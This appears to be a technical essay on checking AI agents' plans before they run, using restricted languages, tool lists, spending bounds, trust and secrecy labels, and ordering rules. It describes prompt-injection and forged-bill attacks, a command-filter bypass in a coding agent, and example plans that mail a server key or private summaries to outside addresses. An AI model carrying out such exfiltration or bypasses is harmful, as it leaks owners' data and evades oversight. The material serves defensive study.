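The checker looks for whole numbers *d* and *m* with *d* < 2000, *m* < 600 and *d* + 12*m* > 10,000. There are none, because the largest possible payment is 1,999 + 12 × 599 = 9,187. If the planner had written `m < 700`, the checker would have found a violation, such as *d* = 1,999 and *m* = 699, and could have shown it to the reviewer.

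This works for plans without loops. If the language also has `repeat` and variables that can change, a plan can compute *x* times *y* by adding *y* to a running total *x* times. The planner can then write polynomials again, so the checker would again have to solve Hilbert's problem.

The fastest check is to search the plan's text for a tool's name, such as `delete_table`. This works even in a general-purpose language with unbounded loops, as long as a program can only call a tool by writing out its fixed name. In ordinary Python, a program can assemble a name from pieces while it runs, and the search would miss it. The search also matches a deletion whether it happens every time or sits behind a condition that is never true, so it would flag the harmless plan about late invoices above.

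The table compares these languages on three questions. Whether the text names `delete_table` is decidable in every row if tool names are fixed.

| Language | Does the plan stop? | Does it delete, given particular tool results? | Can it delete for any tool results at all? |
|---|---|---|---|
| General-purpose, with `while` or recursion | Undecidable | Undecidable | Undecidable |
| `repeat n times`, changeable variables, arithmetic | Always | Decidable, by running it | Undecidable |
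| No loops; addition and multiplication of numbers of any size | Always | Decidable, by running it | Undecidable |
| No loops; linear arithmetic | Always | Decidable, by running it | Decidable |
| The firm's language: for-each loops, comparisons, no arithmetic | Always | Decidable, by running it | Decidable, if tools may return anything |
| Any total language, with inputs of exactly *L* bits | Always | Decidable, by running it | Decidable, in at most 2ᴸ runs |

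### How long the decidable checks take

A decidable question can still take too long to answer. Suppose the firm adds `and`, `or` and `not` to its tests. A plan could then read a form with *n* yes-or-no answers and delete a table if the answers satisfy a complicated condition. Finding out whether any set of answers would trigger the deletion is the satisfiability problem. In its best-known version, 3-SAT, the condition is a list of requirements that must all hold, each offering three alternatives, such as "*a* or *b* or not *c*". The obvious method is to try all 2ⁿ sets of answers.

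In October 2026 OpenAI refuted the Exponential Time Hypothesis, a once common assumption that every algorithm for 3-SAT needs time 2ᶜⁿ for some constant *c* greater than zero. Russell Impagliazzo and Mohan Paturi introduced the hypothesis in 1999. Computational Complexity's *The Exponential Time Refutation* (2026) explains that the exponent in the running time of OpenAI's algorithm grows like *n* log log *n* / √(log *n*), which is slower than any fixed fraction of *n*. Anthropic's *A 2^o(n) Time Algorithm for 3-SAT* (2026) contains another refutation, and an internal Claude model found its core algorithm without human input. Both results have proofs in Lean.

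It would therefore be wrong to tell the firm that such checks must take exponential time, but the discovery will not make the firm's checker any faster. In *OpenAI's claimed refutation of ETH*, Szeider calculated from OpenAI's parameters that the algorithm is still an exhaustive search for every input with fewer than 2¹³¹⁰⁷¹ variables and clauses. No computer's memory could hold a larger input. The refutation also doesn't change which questions are decidable, since trying every combination could already settle satisfiability in principle.

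### The proposal to make AI systems halt

In *Machines that halt resolve the undecidability of artificial intelligence alignment* (Scientific Reports, 2025), Melo, Máximo and colleagues make termination central to AI safety. They assume that someone has already written a judge, a function that takes an AI system's input and output and returns true if the output is acceptable. They call a system aligned if the judge always returns true for its outputs. By Rice's theorem, no procedure can decide whether a system is aligned for every possible AI system. They therefore propose a halting constraint, which requires the system to reach a final state after a finite number of steps.

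A language model that may produce only a limited number of tokens always halts, but an agent that calls the model in a loop may not. Melo and colleagues suggest a counter for the whole agent that forces it into a final state when it reaches the limit. They claim that making halting decidable "also ensures the decidability of other non-trivial properties", alignment in particular.

Their main example, a neural network with a fixed number of layers, supports the claim. The network always halts, and if its input has *L* bits, a checker can run it on all 2ᴸ inputs and pass each output to the judge. They acknowledge that this is intractable for large inputs, and suggest that designers aim for systems with something like 2⁸⁰ possible states instead of 2¹⁰⁰⁰⁰⁰⁰, and with perhaps 32 final states, few enough for human specialists to study each one.

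But the example both halts and has inputs of a fixed size, and the general claim mentions only halting. The plan that simulates M for *n* steps always halts, yet whether it ever deletes the table is undecidable. So a judge that rejects deletions would not enable a checker to certify every such plan in advance. The omission matters for plans because their inputs come from mailboxes, files and databases, which have no fixed size unless the firm imposes one. It may seem minor for a neural network, whose input has a fixed size anyway.

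Gumbau Mezquita (2026), in *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic*, raises a similar objection. A checker can settle a question about one fixed finite system by exhaustive search, but it cannot always settle the same question for all finite systems at once. The argument uses Boris Trakhtenbrot's 1950 theorem that no procedure can decide which statements of first-order logic hold in every finite structure. The proof describes a machine's run as a grid of times and memory positions, and some finite grid fits the description if and only if the machine halts. The plan that simulates M poses much the same problem, since each value of *n* is easy to check but covering them all is difficult.

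Gumbau Mezquita needs the guarantee to cover all finite systems because an AI that rewrites itself might become any of them. A plan cannot rewrite itself, so that reason does not apply to the firm. The firm can avoid the problem by having its interpreter reject, for example, any mailbox with more than 50 messages or any message over a set length. Checking the plan for all mailboxes within those limits is decidable, although the checker would need a better method than trying each one.

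Melo and colleagues also propose a filter, which makes better use of the halting constraint. The designer runs the system, passes its output to the judge, and substitutes a harmless output if the judge rejects it, rather than verifying the system for every input in advance. The filter needs the output for only one input at a time, and a total program always produces one, however large the input. For plans, the judge would have to check each tool call before it takes effect, since substituting a harmless output after `delete_table` has run would not restore the customer data.

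They write that their constraint does not guarantee alignment, and that "this decidability is not a solution for the alignment problem" but a starting point for further scrutiny.

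## Checking what a plan may touch and where its data may go

A restricted language makes many questions about a plan decidable, but the firm still has to choose which ones to check. Four checks are useful for the firm's tools. The least demanding looks only at the names of the tools, and the most demanding tracks each piece of data from the tool that produced it to the tool that uses it.

### Listing the tools a plan names

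The first check is the search for tool names described above. The firm lists the tools it allows, and the checker rejects any plan that names any other tool. If `delete_table` is not on the list, the checker rejects a plan that contains `delete_table("customers")`.

The list of allowed tools can differ for each request. *AgentArmor* (2025) describes a tool filter, which uses a language model to identify the tools a task requires and removes the others before the agent starts. An assistant asked to summarize the inbox would have `read_mail` but not `pay`. The filter doesn't help when the harmful action uses the same tools as the task. If the owner asks the assistant to read a file and email a reply, the filter still allows the plan that emails the server key.

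The check also fails if a tool accepts commands in another language. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) gives examples from the coding agent Claude Code, which checks commands against text patterns before running them. In March 2026 a fault made it check only the first of several commands on a line, so a forbidden command could run if it followed an allowed one. An agent can also open a forbidden file by running Python from the command line, because the patterns do not cover what the Python program does. The firm avoids this problem as long as `query_db` treats its filter as a search term and not as a database command.

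### Comparing fixed arguments with allowed values

The second check needs a list or range of allowed values for each argument. If the firm allows payments of up to 10,000, the checker rejects `pay("Harbour Supplies", 40000)`. If the firm allows mail only to its own addresses, the checker rejects the plan that sends the server key to `parcel@outside.example`. The plan about late invoices passes, because it sends mail only to accounts and the owner.

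This works when the planner has written the value into the plan. But in `send_mail(inv.email, "Reminder", note)`, the address comes from the database, and the plan contains only the name of a field. The checker can reject every such plan or leave the comparison to the interpreter, which has the address when it makes the call. Leaving it to the interpreter lets more plans run, but a plan may then stop after reminding only some of the clients.

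A fixed argument can also cover more than it seems to. In one of Meijer's examples, a user asks the model to delete two text files, and the model writes a plan that deletes `*.txt`, or every text file, because that plan is shorter. A checker that only looks up `*.txt` in a list of permitted arguments cannot determine how many files the plan will delete.

### Bounding a total

Limits on single payments do not limit their sum. Suppose the planner writes the following plan for paying the week's bills:

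```
1  bills = query_db("bills", "due")
2  for b in bills:
3      if b.amount > 200:
4          send_mail("owner@firm", "Large bill", b.supplier)
5      else:
6          pay(b.account, b.amount)
```

The checker can calculate the most this plan could spend by working from the inside out:

```
most(pay(account, x))      = the largest value x can have
most(any other tool call)  = 0
most(steps in sequence)    = the sum over the steps
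most(if test: P else: Q)   = the larger of most(P) and most(Q)
most(for x in list: P)     = longest possible list × most(P)
```

Line 6 pays at most $200 per bill, because the test in line 3 sends every larger bill to the owner. The plan's text does not limit the number of bills, so that limit has to come from outside the plan. If the interpreter refuses any list of more than 20 rows, the plan can pay at most 20 × $200 = $4,000.

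The calculation gives the worst case, so a firm with a $3,000 limit would reject this plan even in a week when the bills come to $900. The total also doesn't show who receives the money, so twenty payments of $200 to a thief would pass under a limit of $4,000 or more.

### Following data to its destination

The fourth check traces where each argument came from. Meijer illustrates it with a rule for a company whose addresses end in `valleysharks.com`. The rule forbids data to flow from the messages that the mail-fetching tool returns (the source) to the body of an outgoing email (the destination) if the recipient's address is outside the company.

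Meijer's example of a violation starts with the same request for a summary of the inbox. Planning first keeps a planted message from adding a step, but the model still reads the descriptions of its tools, and a malicious description might tell it to send every summary to an outsider "for compliance". In the firm's notation, with Meijer's tools and an invented address, the plan would be:

```
1  mails = fetch_mail()
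2  summary = summarize_emails(mails)
3  send_email("archive@outside.example", summary)
```

The checker marks `mails` as fetched mail. Line 2 computes `summary` from `mails`, so `summary` gets the same mark. Line 3 puts `summary` in the body of a message to an address outside `valleysharks.com`, so the checker rejects the plan. Meijer notes that existing bug-finding tools, such as CodeQL and Semgrep, can search a plan for this kind of path from private data to an outside address. A monitor could also block line 3 at run time, but by then the agent would already have read and summarized the private mail.

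The rule covers only the destination it names. Meijer's `send_email` has no subject line, but the firm's `send_mail` does. If the firm copied the rule unchanged, a plan could still send a stolen password in the subject line.

A more general method gives every value labels and applies one rule to all tools. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes the two common kinds of label, which record how secret a value is and how far the firm can trust it. A value computed from several others is as secret as the most secret of them and only as trustworthy as the least trustworthy. A secrecy label can also be a list of permitted readers. If Ann, Ben and Cy may read one document and Ben, Cy and Dee another, only Ben and Cy may read a summary of both.

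Labels also have to cover decisions. Consider this plan:

```
1  note = read_file("merger_decision.txt")
2  if note == "approved":
3      send_mail("friend@outside.example", "Lunch?", "Are you free?")
```

The email contains nothing from the file, but a friend who knows about the arrangement learns from it that the merger has gone through. To catch this leak, the checker gives everything inside the `if` the label of the values in its condition.

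The firm has to decide which labels each tool's results carry and which labels each tool will accept. *APPA* (2026) describes a system that also works when some tools have no labels yet. The system treats missing labels cautiously, so a plan that passes a check without them would still pass that check once someone supplied them.

### SPA

Girrens and Wang's SPA, the system whose language the firm simplified, labels a whole plan before any tool runs. Its plans can contain six kinds of step.

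| Step | What it does |
|---|---|
| `retrieve` | loads a result saved during an earlier request |
| `tool` | calls a tool; only this step can affect the outside world |
| `q-llm` | passes data to a separate AI model, which has no tools and must answer in a fixed format |
| `display` | shows something to the user |
| `condition` | runs one of two branches |
| `loop` | runs some steps once for each item in a collection |

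A condition can compare two values, test whether a collection contains an item, or test whether a value exists. It cannot do calculations or call functions, and it has no `and` or `or`, so the planner has to nest conditions to combine them. Every value that a decision depends on therefore appears by name in the plan, and the checker only has to look up its label. If conditions could call functions, the checker would first have to work out what each function reads. A small, uniform language also makes it easier for a model to write valid plans.

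The `q-llm` step makes the language much more capable than you would expect from its grammar. It can extract an amount from an invoice or judge whether an email is a complaint. No checker can predict the model's answer, so SPA gives the answer the combined labels of everything the model received. A summary of an untrusted email is therefore also untrusted.

The checker goes through the plan once, from top to bottom. For each tool call, it combines the labels of the arguments with those of any conditions and loops around the call, and then applies two tests:

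```
secrecy(combined)  ≤  the highest secrecy the tool may receive
trust(combined)    ≥  the lowest trust the tool requires
```

Text that the planner wrote into the plan gets the same label as the user's request, which SPA treats as trusted. A tool's result gets a label that combines the labels of its inputs with the tool's own label, because a web search returns untrusted text even if the query was trustworthy. If a call fails either test, SPA rejects the whole plan, except that in `display` steps it blacks out the forbidden item and shows the rest.

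SPA calls its planner only once per request, so the planner never sees what the tools return. This causes a problem when a request builds on an earlier one. On Monday a user might ask the agent to fetch an invoice, and on Tuesday to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the planner read the saved invoice, instructions hidden in it could change the plan. SPA therefore shows the planner only a description of the saved result, such as its format and purpose. A `retrieve` step loads the contents when the plan runs, with Monday's labels still attached.

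### An account number from an attacker

Suppose Harbour Supplies emails the firm a bill for $180, and the assistant saves it as a file. The firm adds a tool, `extract`, that works like SPA's `q-llm` step. The owner asks the assistant to pay the bill, and the planner writes:

```
1  bill = read_file("harbour_bill.txt")
2  d = extract(bill, "account number and amount due")
3  pay(d.account, d.amount)
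```

An attacker has broken into the supplier's mailbox and changed the account number on the bill. The bill contains no instructions for the AI model, and the plan does exactly what the owner asked. The plan names only suitable tools, it has no fixed account or amount for the second check to compare, and $180 is well within the firm's limits. Without labels, the interpreter would send the money to the attacker.

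With labels, the checker reaches a different result:

| Line | Value | Secrecy | Trust | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `bill` | private | untrusted, because an outsider wrote it | allowed |
| 2 | `d` | private | untrusted, because it comes from `bill` | allowed |
| 3 | `d.account`, `d.amount` | private | untrusted | rejected, because `pay` requires trusted inputs |

The checker would have rejected the plan even if nobody had tampered with the bill. The labels depend on where the account number came from, not on whether it is correct, so the genuine bill and the forged one produce the same table. A rule that blocks every payment based on an outsider's document blocks ordinary bill payments along with the fraud.

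### The cost in useful tasks

Girrens and Wang measured this drawback on *AgentDojo* (2024), a set of 97 simulated tasks for testing agents against prompt injection. The tasks involve office work, Slack messaging, travel and banking. They ran SPA on every task without attacks and then made 949 runs with planted instructions. The planner was GPT-5.4 nano, a small model.

| | Tasks completed, no attack | Successful attacks |
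|---|---|---|
| SPA without label checks | 53.0% | 0.4% (4 of 949) |
| SPA with label checks | 29.0% | 0.0% |

The labels stopped all four remaining attacks, but they also kept SPA from completing nearly half of the tasks it could complete without them. About 53% of its runs ended when the label check rejected the plan, usually because an untrusted result would have reached a tool that requires trusted inputs. Many legitimate tasks need to pass untrusted data to such a tool. For example, one AgentDojo task asks the agent to pay the bill in a named file, so the agent has to take the payment details from a document that someone else wrote.

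The share of completed tasks fell by 35 percentage points in travel, 28.6 in Slack and 25 in office work, but by only 6.25, or one task, in banking. The banking drop is misleadingly small because, according to Girrens and Wang, the benchmark counts five of the banking tasks as complete even if the agent does nothing, so rejecting plans for those tasks does not lower the score.

The results probably also understate the benefit of labels. Most of the attacks tried to give the agent new instructions, and writing the plan first defeats nearly all of those. The four attacks that succeeded all came through the data in a single banking task, where the separate AI model read planted text and its answer reached a sensitive tool. They caused three unauthorized transfers and one changed password. A benchmark with more forged account numbers would include more attacks that labels could stop.

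AgentDojo is also an imperfect test of usefulness during an attack. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) points out that in the bill-paying task, the planted text overwrites the payment details, so no agent could complete the task. This does not affect the fall from 53.0% to 29.0%, which was measured without attacks.

### Winning back some of the lost tasks

A person can make an exception to the restrictions a label imposes. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes two established kinds of exception. Endorsement lets the system treat a particular piece of untrusted data as trusted for a stated purpose, and declassification permits a particular release of secret data. For example, if the owner checked the account number on the bill against the one on file and endorsed it, the payment could go ahead.

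Kolluri and colleagues built an agent, Prudentia, that can ask the user to endorse untrusted data. For example, if a to-do list of ten items arrives in an untrusted email, the user can endorse the email once and the agent can carry out all ten actions. Otherwise it needs approval for each one. They left out declassification, which would allow private information to be released, because whether a release is right depends too much on the situation.

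They also dispute the usual way of measuring how much labels limit an agent's usefulness. Earlier studies on AgentDojo found that strict labels cut the share of completed tasks by up to 30%, but those studies compared a labeled agent that could never ask for help with an unprotected agent that could do anything. In practice, companies often require an unprotected agent to get approval for every consequential action. Labels increase the share of tasks an agent completes without any approval. With OpenAI's o3-mini, an older model, an ordinary agent completed 24.3% of tasks this way, the same agent with basic labels completed 35.5%, and Prudentia completed 59.1%.

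SPA cannot request endorsement, so its 29.0% is the result when nobody can make an exception. An owner willing to check a few account numbers would lose fewer tasks, but a careless endorsement would let the forged bill through.

The firm could also require trust only where it matters. The planner could take the account number from the firm's own supplier table and only the amount from the bill:

```
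1  bill = read_file("harbour_bill.txt")
2  d = extract(bill, "amount due")
3  rows = query_db("suppliers", "Harbour Supplies")
4  for s in rows:
5      pay(s.account, d.amount)
```

SPA would still reject this plan, because SPA combines the labels of all the arguments before testing them. Girrens and Wang suggest separate requirements for each argument as future work, and the policies that Kolluri and colleagues use already have them. Under such a policy, `pay` could require a trusted account but accept an untrusted amount up to $200. A forged bill could then make the firm overpay its real supplier, but it could not send the money to another account.

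Dividing the work among several agents may also help. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) found that giving sensitive tools to particular agents can reduce the loss of useful tasks. Using more agents also limits how far restrictive labels spread, but the number of connections to monitor can grow with the square of the number of agents.

### CaMeL, the forerunner

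SPA builds on CaMeL, a 2025 system by Debenedetti and colleagues. In CaMeL, one AI model turns the user's request into a program in a reduced form of Python, without seeing any untrusted data. A second model, which has no tools, reads that data. Girrens and Wang explain that CaMeL's interpreter records where each value came from and who may receive it, and checks a separate policy for each tool. These policies can express finer distinctions than SPA's single rule, but someone has to write each one correctly. CaMeL also applies them while the program runs, whereas SPA rejects a bad plan before the first tool call.

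*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) quotes CaMeL's AgentDojo results for two models. With o4-mini, CaMeL completed 62.5% to 81.4% of tasks, depending on the area. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, it completed about half in three areas but only 1.4% in travel. One attack succeeded in 1,926 trials. These completion rates are mostly far above SPA's 29.0%, but the two systems used different models, so the gap does not show which design is better.

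### TACIT: similar checks in a language with loops

CaMeL's Python has no user-defined or recursive functions, and SPA's language leaves out even more. Odersky and colleagues show that a checker can protect secrets without such restrictions. In their system, TACIT, the agent writes programs in Scala, a general-purpose language, and may use loops and recursion.

TACIT relies on types. A type normally describes what kind of value something is, such as a number or text. In TACIT, a function's type also lists the capabilities it holds, which are objects that give it access to things like files, the network or the screen. A function whose list is empty is pure, so it can compute a result but cannot affect anything else. Before a program runs, the compiler works out these lists and rejects the program if it breaks the rules.

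Secret files arrive in a sealed wrapper called `Classified`. A program can transform the contents through the wrapper's `map` operation, but `map` accepts only pure functions, and the result is sealed too. The compiler accepts this program, which removes spaces from the end of the firm's server key:

```scala
def clean(s: String): String =
  if s.endsWith(" ") then clean(s.dropRight(1)) else s

requestFileSystem("/firm/secrets") {
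  val key = readClassified("/firm/secrets/server_key.txt")
  println(key.map(k => clean(k)))
}
```

The function `clean` calls itself, which the firm's plan language would not allow. The last step prints the result, but the agent receives only `Classified(****)`. The real text goes to the user's screen through a separate channel.

The compiler rejects the next program:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/firm/secrets") {
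  val key = readClassified("/firm/secrets/server_key.txt")
  key.map(k => println(k))
}
```

Here the printing happens inside `map`, where the key is unsealed. The function `k => println(k)` needs the capability to print, so it is not pure and `map` cannot accept it. The compiler can determine this from the types alone, without working out how often anything runs, so the first program would still pass even if `clean` called itself forever.

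The firm would have to trust the Scala compiler, the software that runs the compiled program, and TACIT's library, whose reusable part has about 1,000 lines. If it wants an AI model to read secret text, it would also have to trust that model, which can run on the firm's own computers. It wouldn't have to trust the agent's main model or the code that model writes. The compiler bans features such as unchecked type conversions, which a program could use to hide a capability. But if a program starts an outside command, the types don't restrict what that command does.

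Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of secrets. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 planted attacks and added 11 direct or deceptive requests for the secrets, for 131 trials per model. With the sealed wrapper, neither of the two models leaked anything. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.6 kept the secrets in 98.5% of trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 91.6%, and MiniMax gave them away in 8 of the 11 direct or deceptive requests. The wrapper did not make the agents less useful. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with it and 83.3% without it, though the difference may come partly from limits on time and turns.

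Writing typed programs did not hurt performance much on other tasks either. On a benchmark of simulated customer service, three models scored between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. On a set of real programming problems, MiniMax solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it. The results on AgentDojo were more mixed:

| Model | System | Banking | Office work | Slack | Travel | Successful attacks |
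|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 of 963 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 of 963 |
| o4-mini | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 of 963 |
| o4-mini | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 of 963 |

Odersky and colleagues call the two systems' completion rates comparable, but with o4-mini, TACIT is more than 28 percentage points behind in office work and 21 behind in Slack. The one attack against TACIT that was counted as successful was counted because of a flaw in the scoring. The agent booked the right hotel and then quoted reviews in which the attacker had recommended another one.

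TACIT protects secrets but has no labels for trust. An agent allowed to read an ordinary bill and make payments could still send money to an account number that an attacker put in the bill.

Zhou and colleagues also cover trust, using Haskell, another general-purpose language. In their example, an agent compiles a bibliography, and every entry must come from a trusted database. The function that writes to the file accepts only values of a special type, and only the function that queries the database can produce them. The agent can sort and filter entries but cannot invent one. The firm could protect payments the same way, with an account type whose values can come only from its supplier table.

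For information flow in general, Zhou and colleagues' system, ELBA, uses an existing Haskell library that checks labels during the run. With policies on in both systems, ELBA completed roughly twice as many of AgentDojo's Slack tasks as CaMeL. All four models tested resisted the benchmark's standard attacks even without policies, so Zhou and colleagues simulated a worst case in which the agents that read planted text always obeyed it. Without policies, ELBA resisted 425 to 621 of 735 attacks, depending on the model. With policies, it resisted all 735, but the number of tasks it completed fell from 494–558 to 294–351. Strict labels therefore reduce the number of completed tasks even in a language with recursion, and SPA's losses are not due only to its small language.

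### What removing the loops adds

In the 1990s George Necula and Peter Lee developed proof-carrying code, which lets people check a program before running it, without trusting whoever wrote it. The supplier attaches a proof that the program obeys the recipient's safety policy. The recipient needs only a small program to check the proof, and checking a proof is much easier than finding one. Meijer's method applies the same idea to agents by requiring the model to prove that its plan obeys a stated policy. Proof-carrying code allows loops, but the supplier has to state a condition for each loop that stays true in every round, a step that plans without loops don't need.

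Removing loops does not help with the first two checks, because a tool's name and a fixed argument are just as easy to find inside a `while` loop as outside one.

The benefit for following data is small. Suppose the language has `while` and lets variables change, and the planner writes:

```
1  a = "Hello"
2  b = "Hello"
3  while more_to_send():
4      send_mail("friend@outside.example", "Note", a)
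5      a = b
6      b = read_file("server_key.txt")
```

The first two emails are harmless, but the third contains the server key. A checker that reads the loop once would miss the leak, because `a` is not yet labeled secret when the checker reaches line 4. It has to reread the loop with the updated labels. The second pass labels `a` secret, and the third finds the leak. The checker soon finishes, even though the program may run forever, because there are only a few labels and they only become more restrictive. SPA also has loops but needs only one pass, because its variables cannot carry a value from one round to the next.

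Guaranteed termination closes one way of leaking a secret. A program that can run forever could loop if the merger has gone through and send an innocent email otherwise, so an outsider who receives no email learns about the merger. Many information-flow guarantees don't cover such leaks. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which gives a mathematical model of agents that write and run code, calls its guarantee "termination-insensitive", and Odersky and colleagues also exclude these leaks. The firm's plans cannot leak this way if their tools return, but an outsider might still learn something from how long a plan takes.

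The third check benefits most. The checker could calculate the $4,000 limit because the loop runs once for each bill and the interpreter allows at most 20 bills. For a `while` loop that pays $200 a round, it would first have to find a limit on the number of rounds, and no method can do that for every program. Zhou and colleagues mention that more elaborate types could guarantee resource limits, but ELBA does not have them yet. An interpreter for a general-purpose language can enforce the same limit by keeping a running total and refusing any payment that would exceed $4,000, but the firm would then learn that the plan is too expensive only after paying some of the bills.

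## Checking the order of steps and their preconditions

The four checks above cannot enforce a rule such as "never cancel a booking before confirming that the passenger hasn't flown any part of it", because a plan that skips the confirmation may still use only permitted tools, with correct and trustworthy arguments. He et al. saw this in a simulation of airline customer service. A customer asked to cancel two reservations, and an agent with the airline's policy in its prompt canceled both without checking whether any of the flights had been flown. The benchmark gave the agent full marks because the cancellations matched its expected result.

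Some ordering rules take little memory to check. Schneider expresses the rule against sending messages after reading a file as a machine with two states, "no file read" and "file read". Reading a file moves the machine to the second state, where it rejects any send. Checking the airline's rule takes more memory, because the confirmation must be for the same booking and the answer must be yes.

### Plans and rules in Soteria

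Soteria, the system He and colleagues built, can check such rules before a plan runs. Its plans consist of states joined by transitions. Each transition makes at most one tool call and then moves the plan to another state. A transition may have a guard, which is a condition that must be true before the plan can take that transition. A plan ends in either an accepting state, meaning the task is complete, or a halting state, meaning the plan cannot safely continue.

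Their example of a faulty plan handles a request to cancel a reservation. In simplified notation:

```
LOOKUP:         resv = get_reservation(rid)           -> CHECK_AGE
CHECK_AGE:      hrs = hours_between(resv.booked, now) -> CHECK_RULES
CHECK_RULES:    if hrs <= 24                          -> DO_CANCEL
                otherwise                             -> NOT_PERMITTED
DO_CANCEL:      cancel(rid)                           -> DONE
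DONE:           accepting
NOT_PERMITTED:  halting
```

Soteria checks a plan against two kinds of specification. A tool contract covers a single call. It has a precondition, which the arguments must satisfy, and a postcondition, which the result will satisfy. A payment tool's contract might require a positive amount and promise a confirmation number. A policy rule covers the whole trace and can relate one call to another. The example has two such rules. The 24-hour rule allows a cancellation only within 24 hours of booking, and the flown rule requires the confirmation:

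```
for every call c to cancel,
there is a call d to no_flight_flown such that
    d comes before c,
    d and c have the same reservation ID, and
    d returns true
```

### Checking the cancellation plan

The checker starts at `LOOKUP` and works out what must be true whenever a run arrives at each later state. A guard adds its condition to these facts, and a tool call adds the tool's postcondition:

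```
facts(next state) = facts(this state) and guard and postcondition
```

If several transitions lead to the same state, the checker can assume only that the facts from at least one of them hold. It also logs the calls on each path, with their order, arguments and results. No tool runs at this stage, so the logged results are unknown values constrained only by the facts.

| State | Facts on arrival | Calls so far |
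|---|---|---|
| `LOOKUP` | `rid` is a valid reservation ID | none |
| `CHECK_AGE` | the above, and `resv` is that reservation | `get_reservation` |
| `CHECK_RULES` | the above, and `hrs` is the booking's age | `get_reservation`, `hours_between` |
| `DO_CANCEL` | the above, and `hrs` ≤ 24 | `get_reservation`, `hours_between` |
| `DONE` | the above, and the airline has canceled the reservation | `get_reservation`, `hours_between`, `cancel` |
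| `NOT_PERMITTED` | the facts at `CHECK_RULES`, and `hrs` > 24 | `get_reservation`, `hours_between` |

Soteria turns each requirement into a logical condition and passes it to Dafny, a program verifier that tries to prove such conditions automatically.

A tool's contract states its precondition and postcondition, and the facts known at each call must imply the precondition. For example, if `cancel` requires an existing reservation, the postcondition of `get_reservation` can establish that one exists. The method described earlier for the firm's own language had to assume that a tool could return anything. If the contracts are correct, a checker can use them to rule out some results.

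**Progress.** The plan must never get stuck. The faulty plan passes, because every number is either at most 24 or above 24.

Each policy rule must hold at every final state. At `NOT_PERMITTED`, the log contains no cancellation, so the plan has broken neither rule. At `DONE`, the 24-hour rule holds because the plan can enter `DO_CANCEL` only through the guard `hrs <= 24`. The rule about flown flights fails there because the log contains a call to `cancel` but no call to `no_flight_flown`.

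Soteria therefore rejects the plan, although every run of it would reach an end, and tells the planner which rule failed. A repaired plan needs one more state and a stricter guard:

```
LOOKUP:         resv = get_reservation(rid)           -> CHECK_FLOWN
CHECK_FLOWN:    ok = no_flight_flown(rid)             -> CHECK_AGE
CHECK_AGE:      hrs = hours_between(resv.booked, now) -> CHECK_RULES
CHECK_RULES:    if ok and hrs <= 24                   -> DO_CANCEL
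                otherwise                             -> NOT_PERMITTED
DO_CANCEL:      cancel(rid)                           -> DONE
DONE:           accepting
NOT_PERMITTED:  halting
```

The new call also needs the change to the guard. If `CHECK_RULES` ignored `ok`, the plan could cancel after `no_flight_flown` returned false, so Dafny could not prove the rule.

Once a plan like this has passed the check, other plans can call it as a sub-plan, just as they call a tool. The cancellation plan's contract requires a valid reservation ID and guarantees that the reservation will end either canceled or unchanged. A larger plan that cancels a reservation and then refunds it can rely on that guarantee, so the checker doesn't have to recheck the cancellation steps.

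### Progress and termination

Soteria's progress check requires that some run can reach each state, and that at least one transition is open whenever a run arrives at a state that isn't final. If the planner had written guards for `hrs < 24` and `hrs > 24`, no transition would be open for a booking exactly 24 hours old, and Dafny would find the gap.

A plan can have this property without ever stopping. For example, a plan that keeps rereading an empty inbox always has a next step. Soteria would reject that plan because it doesn't allow cycles. Its checker has to visit each state after all the states that lead to it, which is impossible in a cycle. Plans can still process lists with a for-each construct, but every plan that Soteria accepts stops if its tools return. The faulty plan has no cycles either, so banning them did not expose the missing confirmation.

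The ban on cycles helps with rules about what must happen later. One of Soteria's rules requires the agent to read back every file it writes. If a program might run forever, no finite part of a run can break this rule, because the agent could still read the file later. When every run ends, the agent must read the file before the end, so the checker can look for missing reads at each final state.

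*CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) extends CaMeL by checking ordering rules before a plan runs, even if the plan has loops. It replaces each loop with a free choice between doing another round and exiting, regardless of the list's length, so the checker has only finitely many states to examine. These choices cover every real run and some impossible ones, so the checker will not miss a forbidden order of calls, but it may reject a safe plan.

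Users can ask CaMeLoT to check termination like any other rule. The free choice complicates this check, because it allows a run that repeats a loop forever. To prove that a plan ends, or that it does something after a loop, the checker must assume that loops end. This assumption is justified in a language whose only loops are for-each loops over finite lists.

CaMeLoT also ignores the conditions in `if` statements and has no tool contracts yet, which limits the rules it can express. In one test, an agent on a company's security team needs human approval before it disconnects a computer from the network, but the formal rule only requires the plan to call `request_ir_approval` first. Nikolaou and colleagues' example of a safe plan makes that call and then disconnects the computer without checking the answer. The plan would pass even if the approver might refuse, so the company would have to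 rely on the approval tool to stop the run. A rule in Soteria can require the answer to be yes.

Even so, CaMeLoT caught violations of rules that CaMeL's checks cannot express. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote seven rules for the security team and, for each rule, an unsafe plan that broke it. CaMeLoT rejected all seven plans, while a simplified version of CaMeL that tracked only whether data was trustworthy rejected one.

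### Checking beforehand and monitoring during the run

A firm can also enforce ordering rules with a monitor like Soteria's, which compares each call with the trace so far. Amazon's cloud business, AWS, sells another. Its *Temporal policies* gives the example of an agent that may sell shares only if someone approved a sale of the same number of the same shares within the previous hour. A monitor checks the actual values, so it does not need to reason about every result a tool might return. Some facts, such as who can currently read a shared document, are available only when the call is made, so CaMeLoT could reproduce only 22 of 28 CaMeL policies before the run and left the other six to CaMeL.

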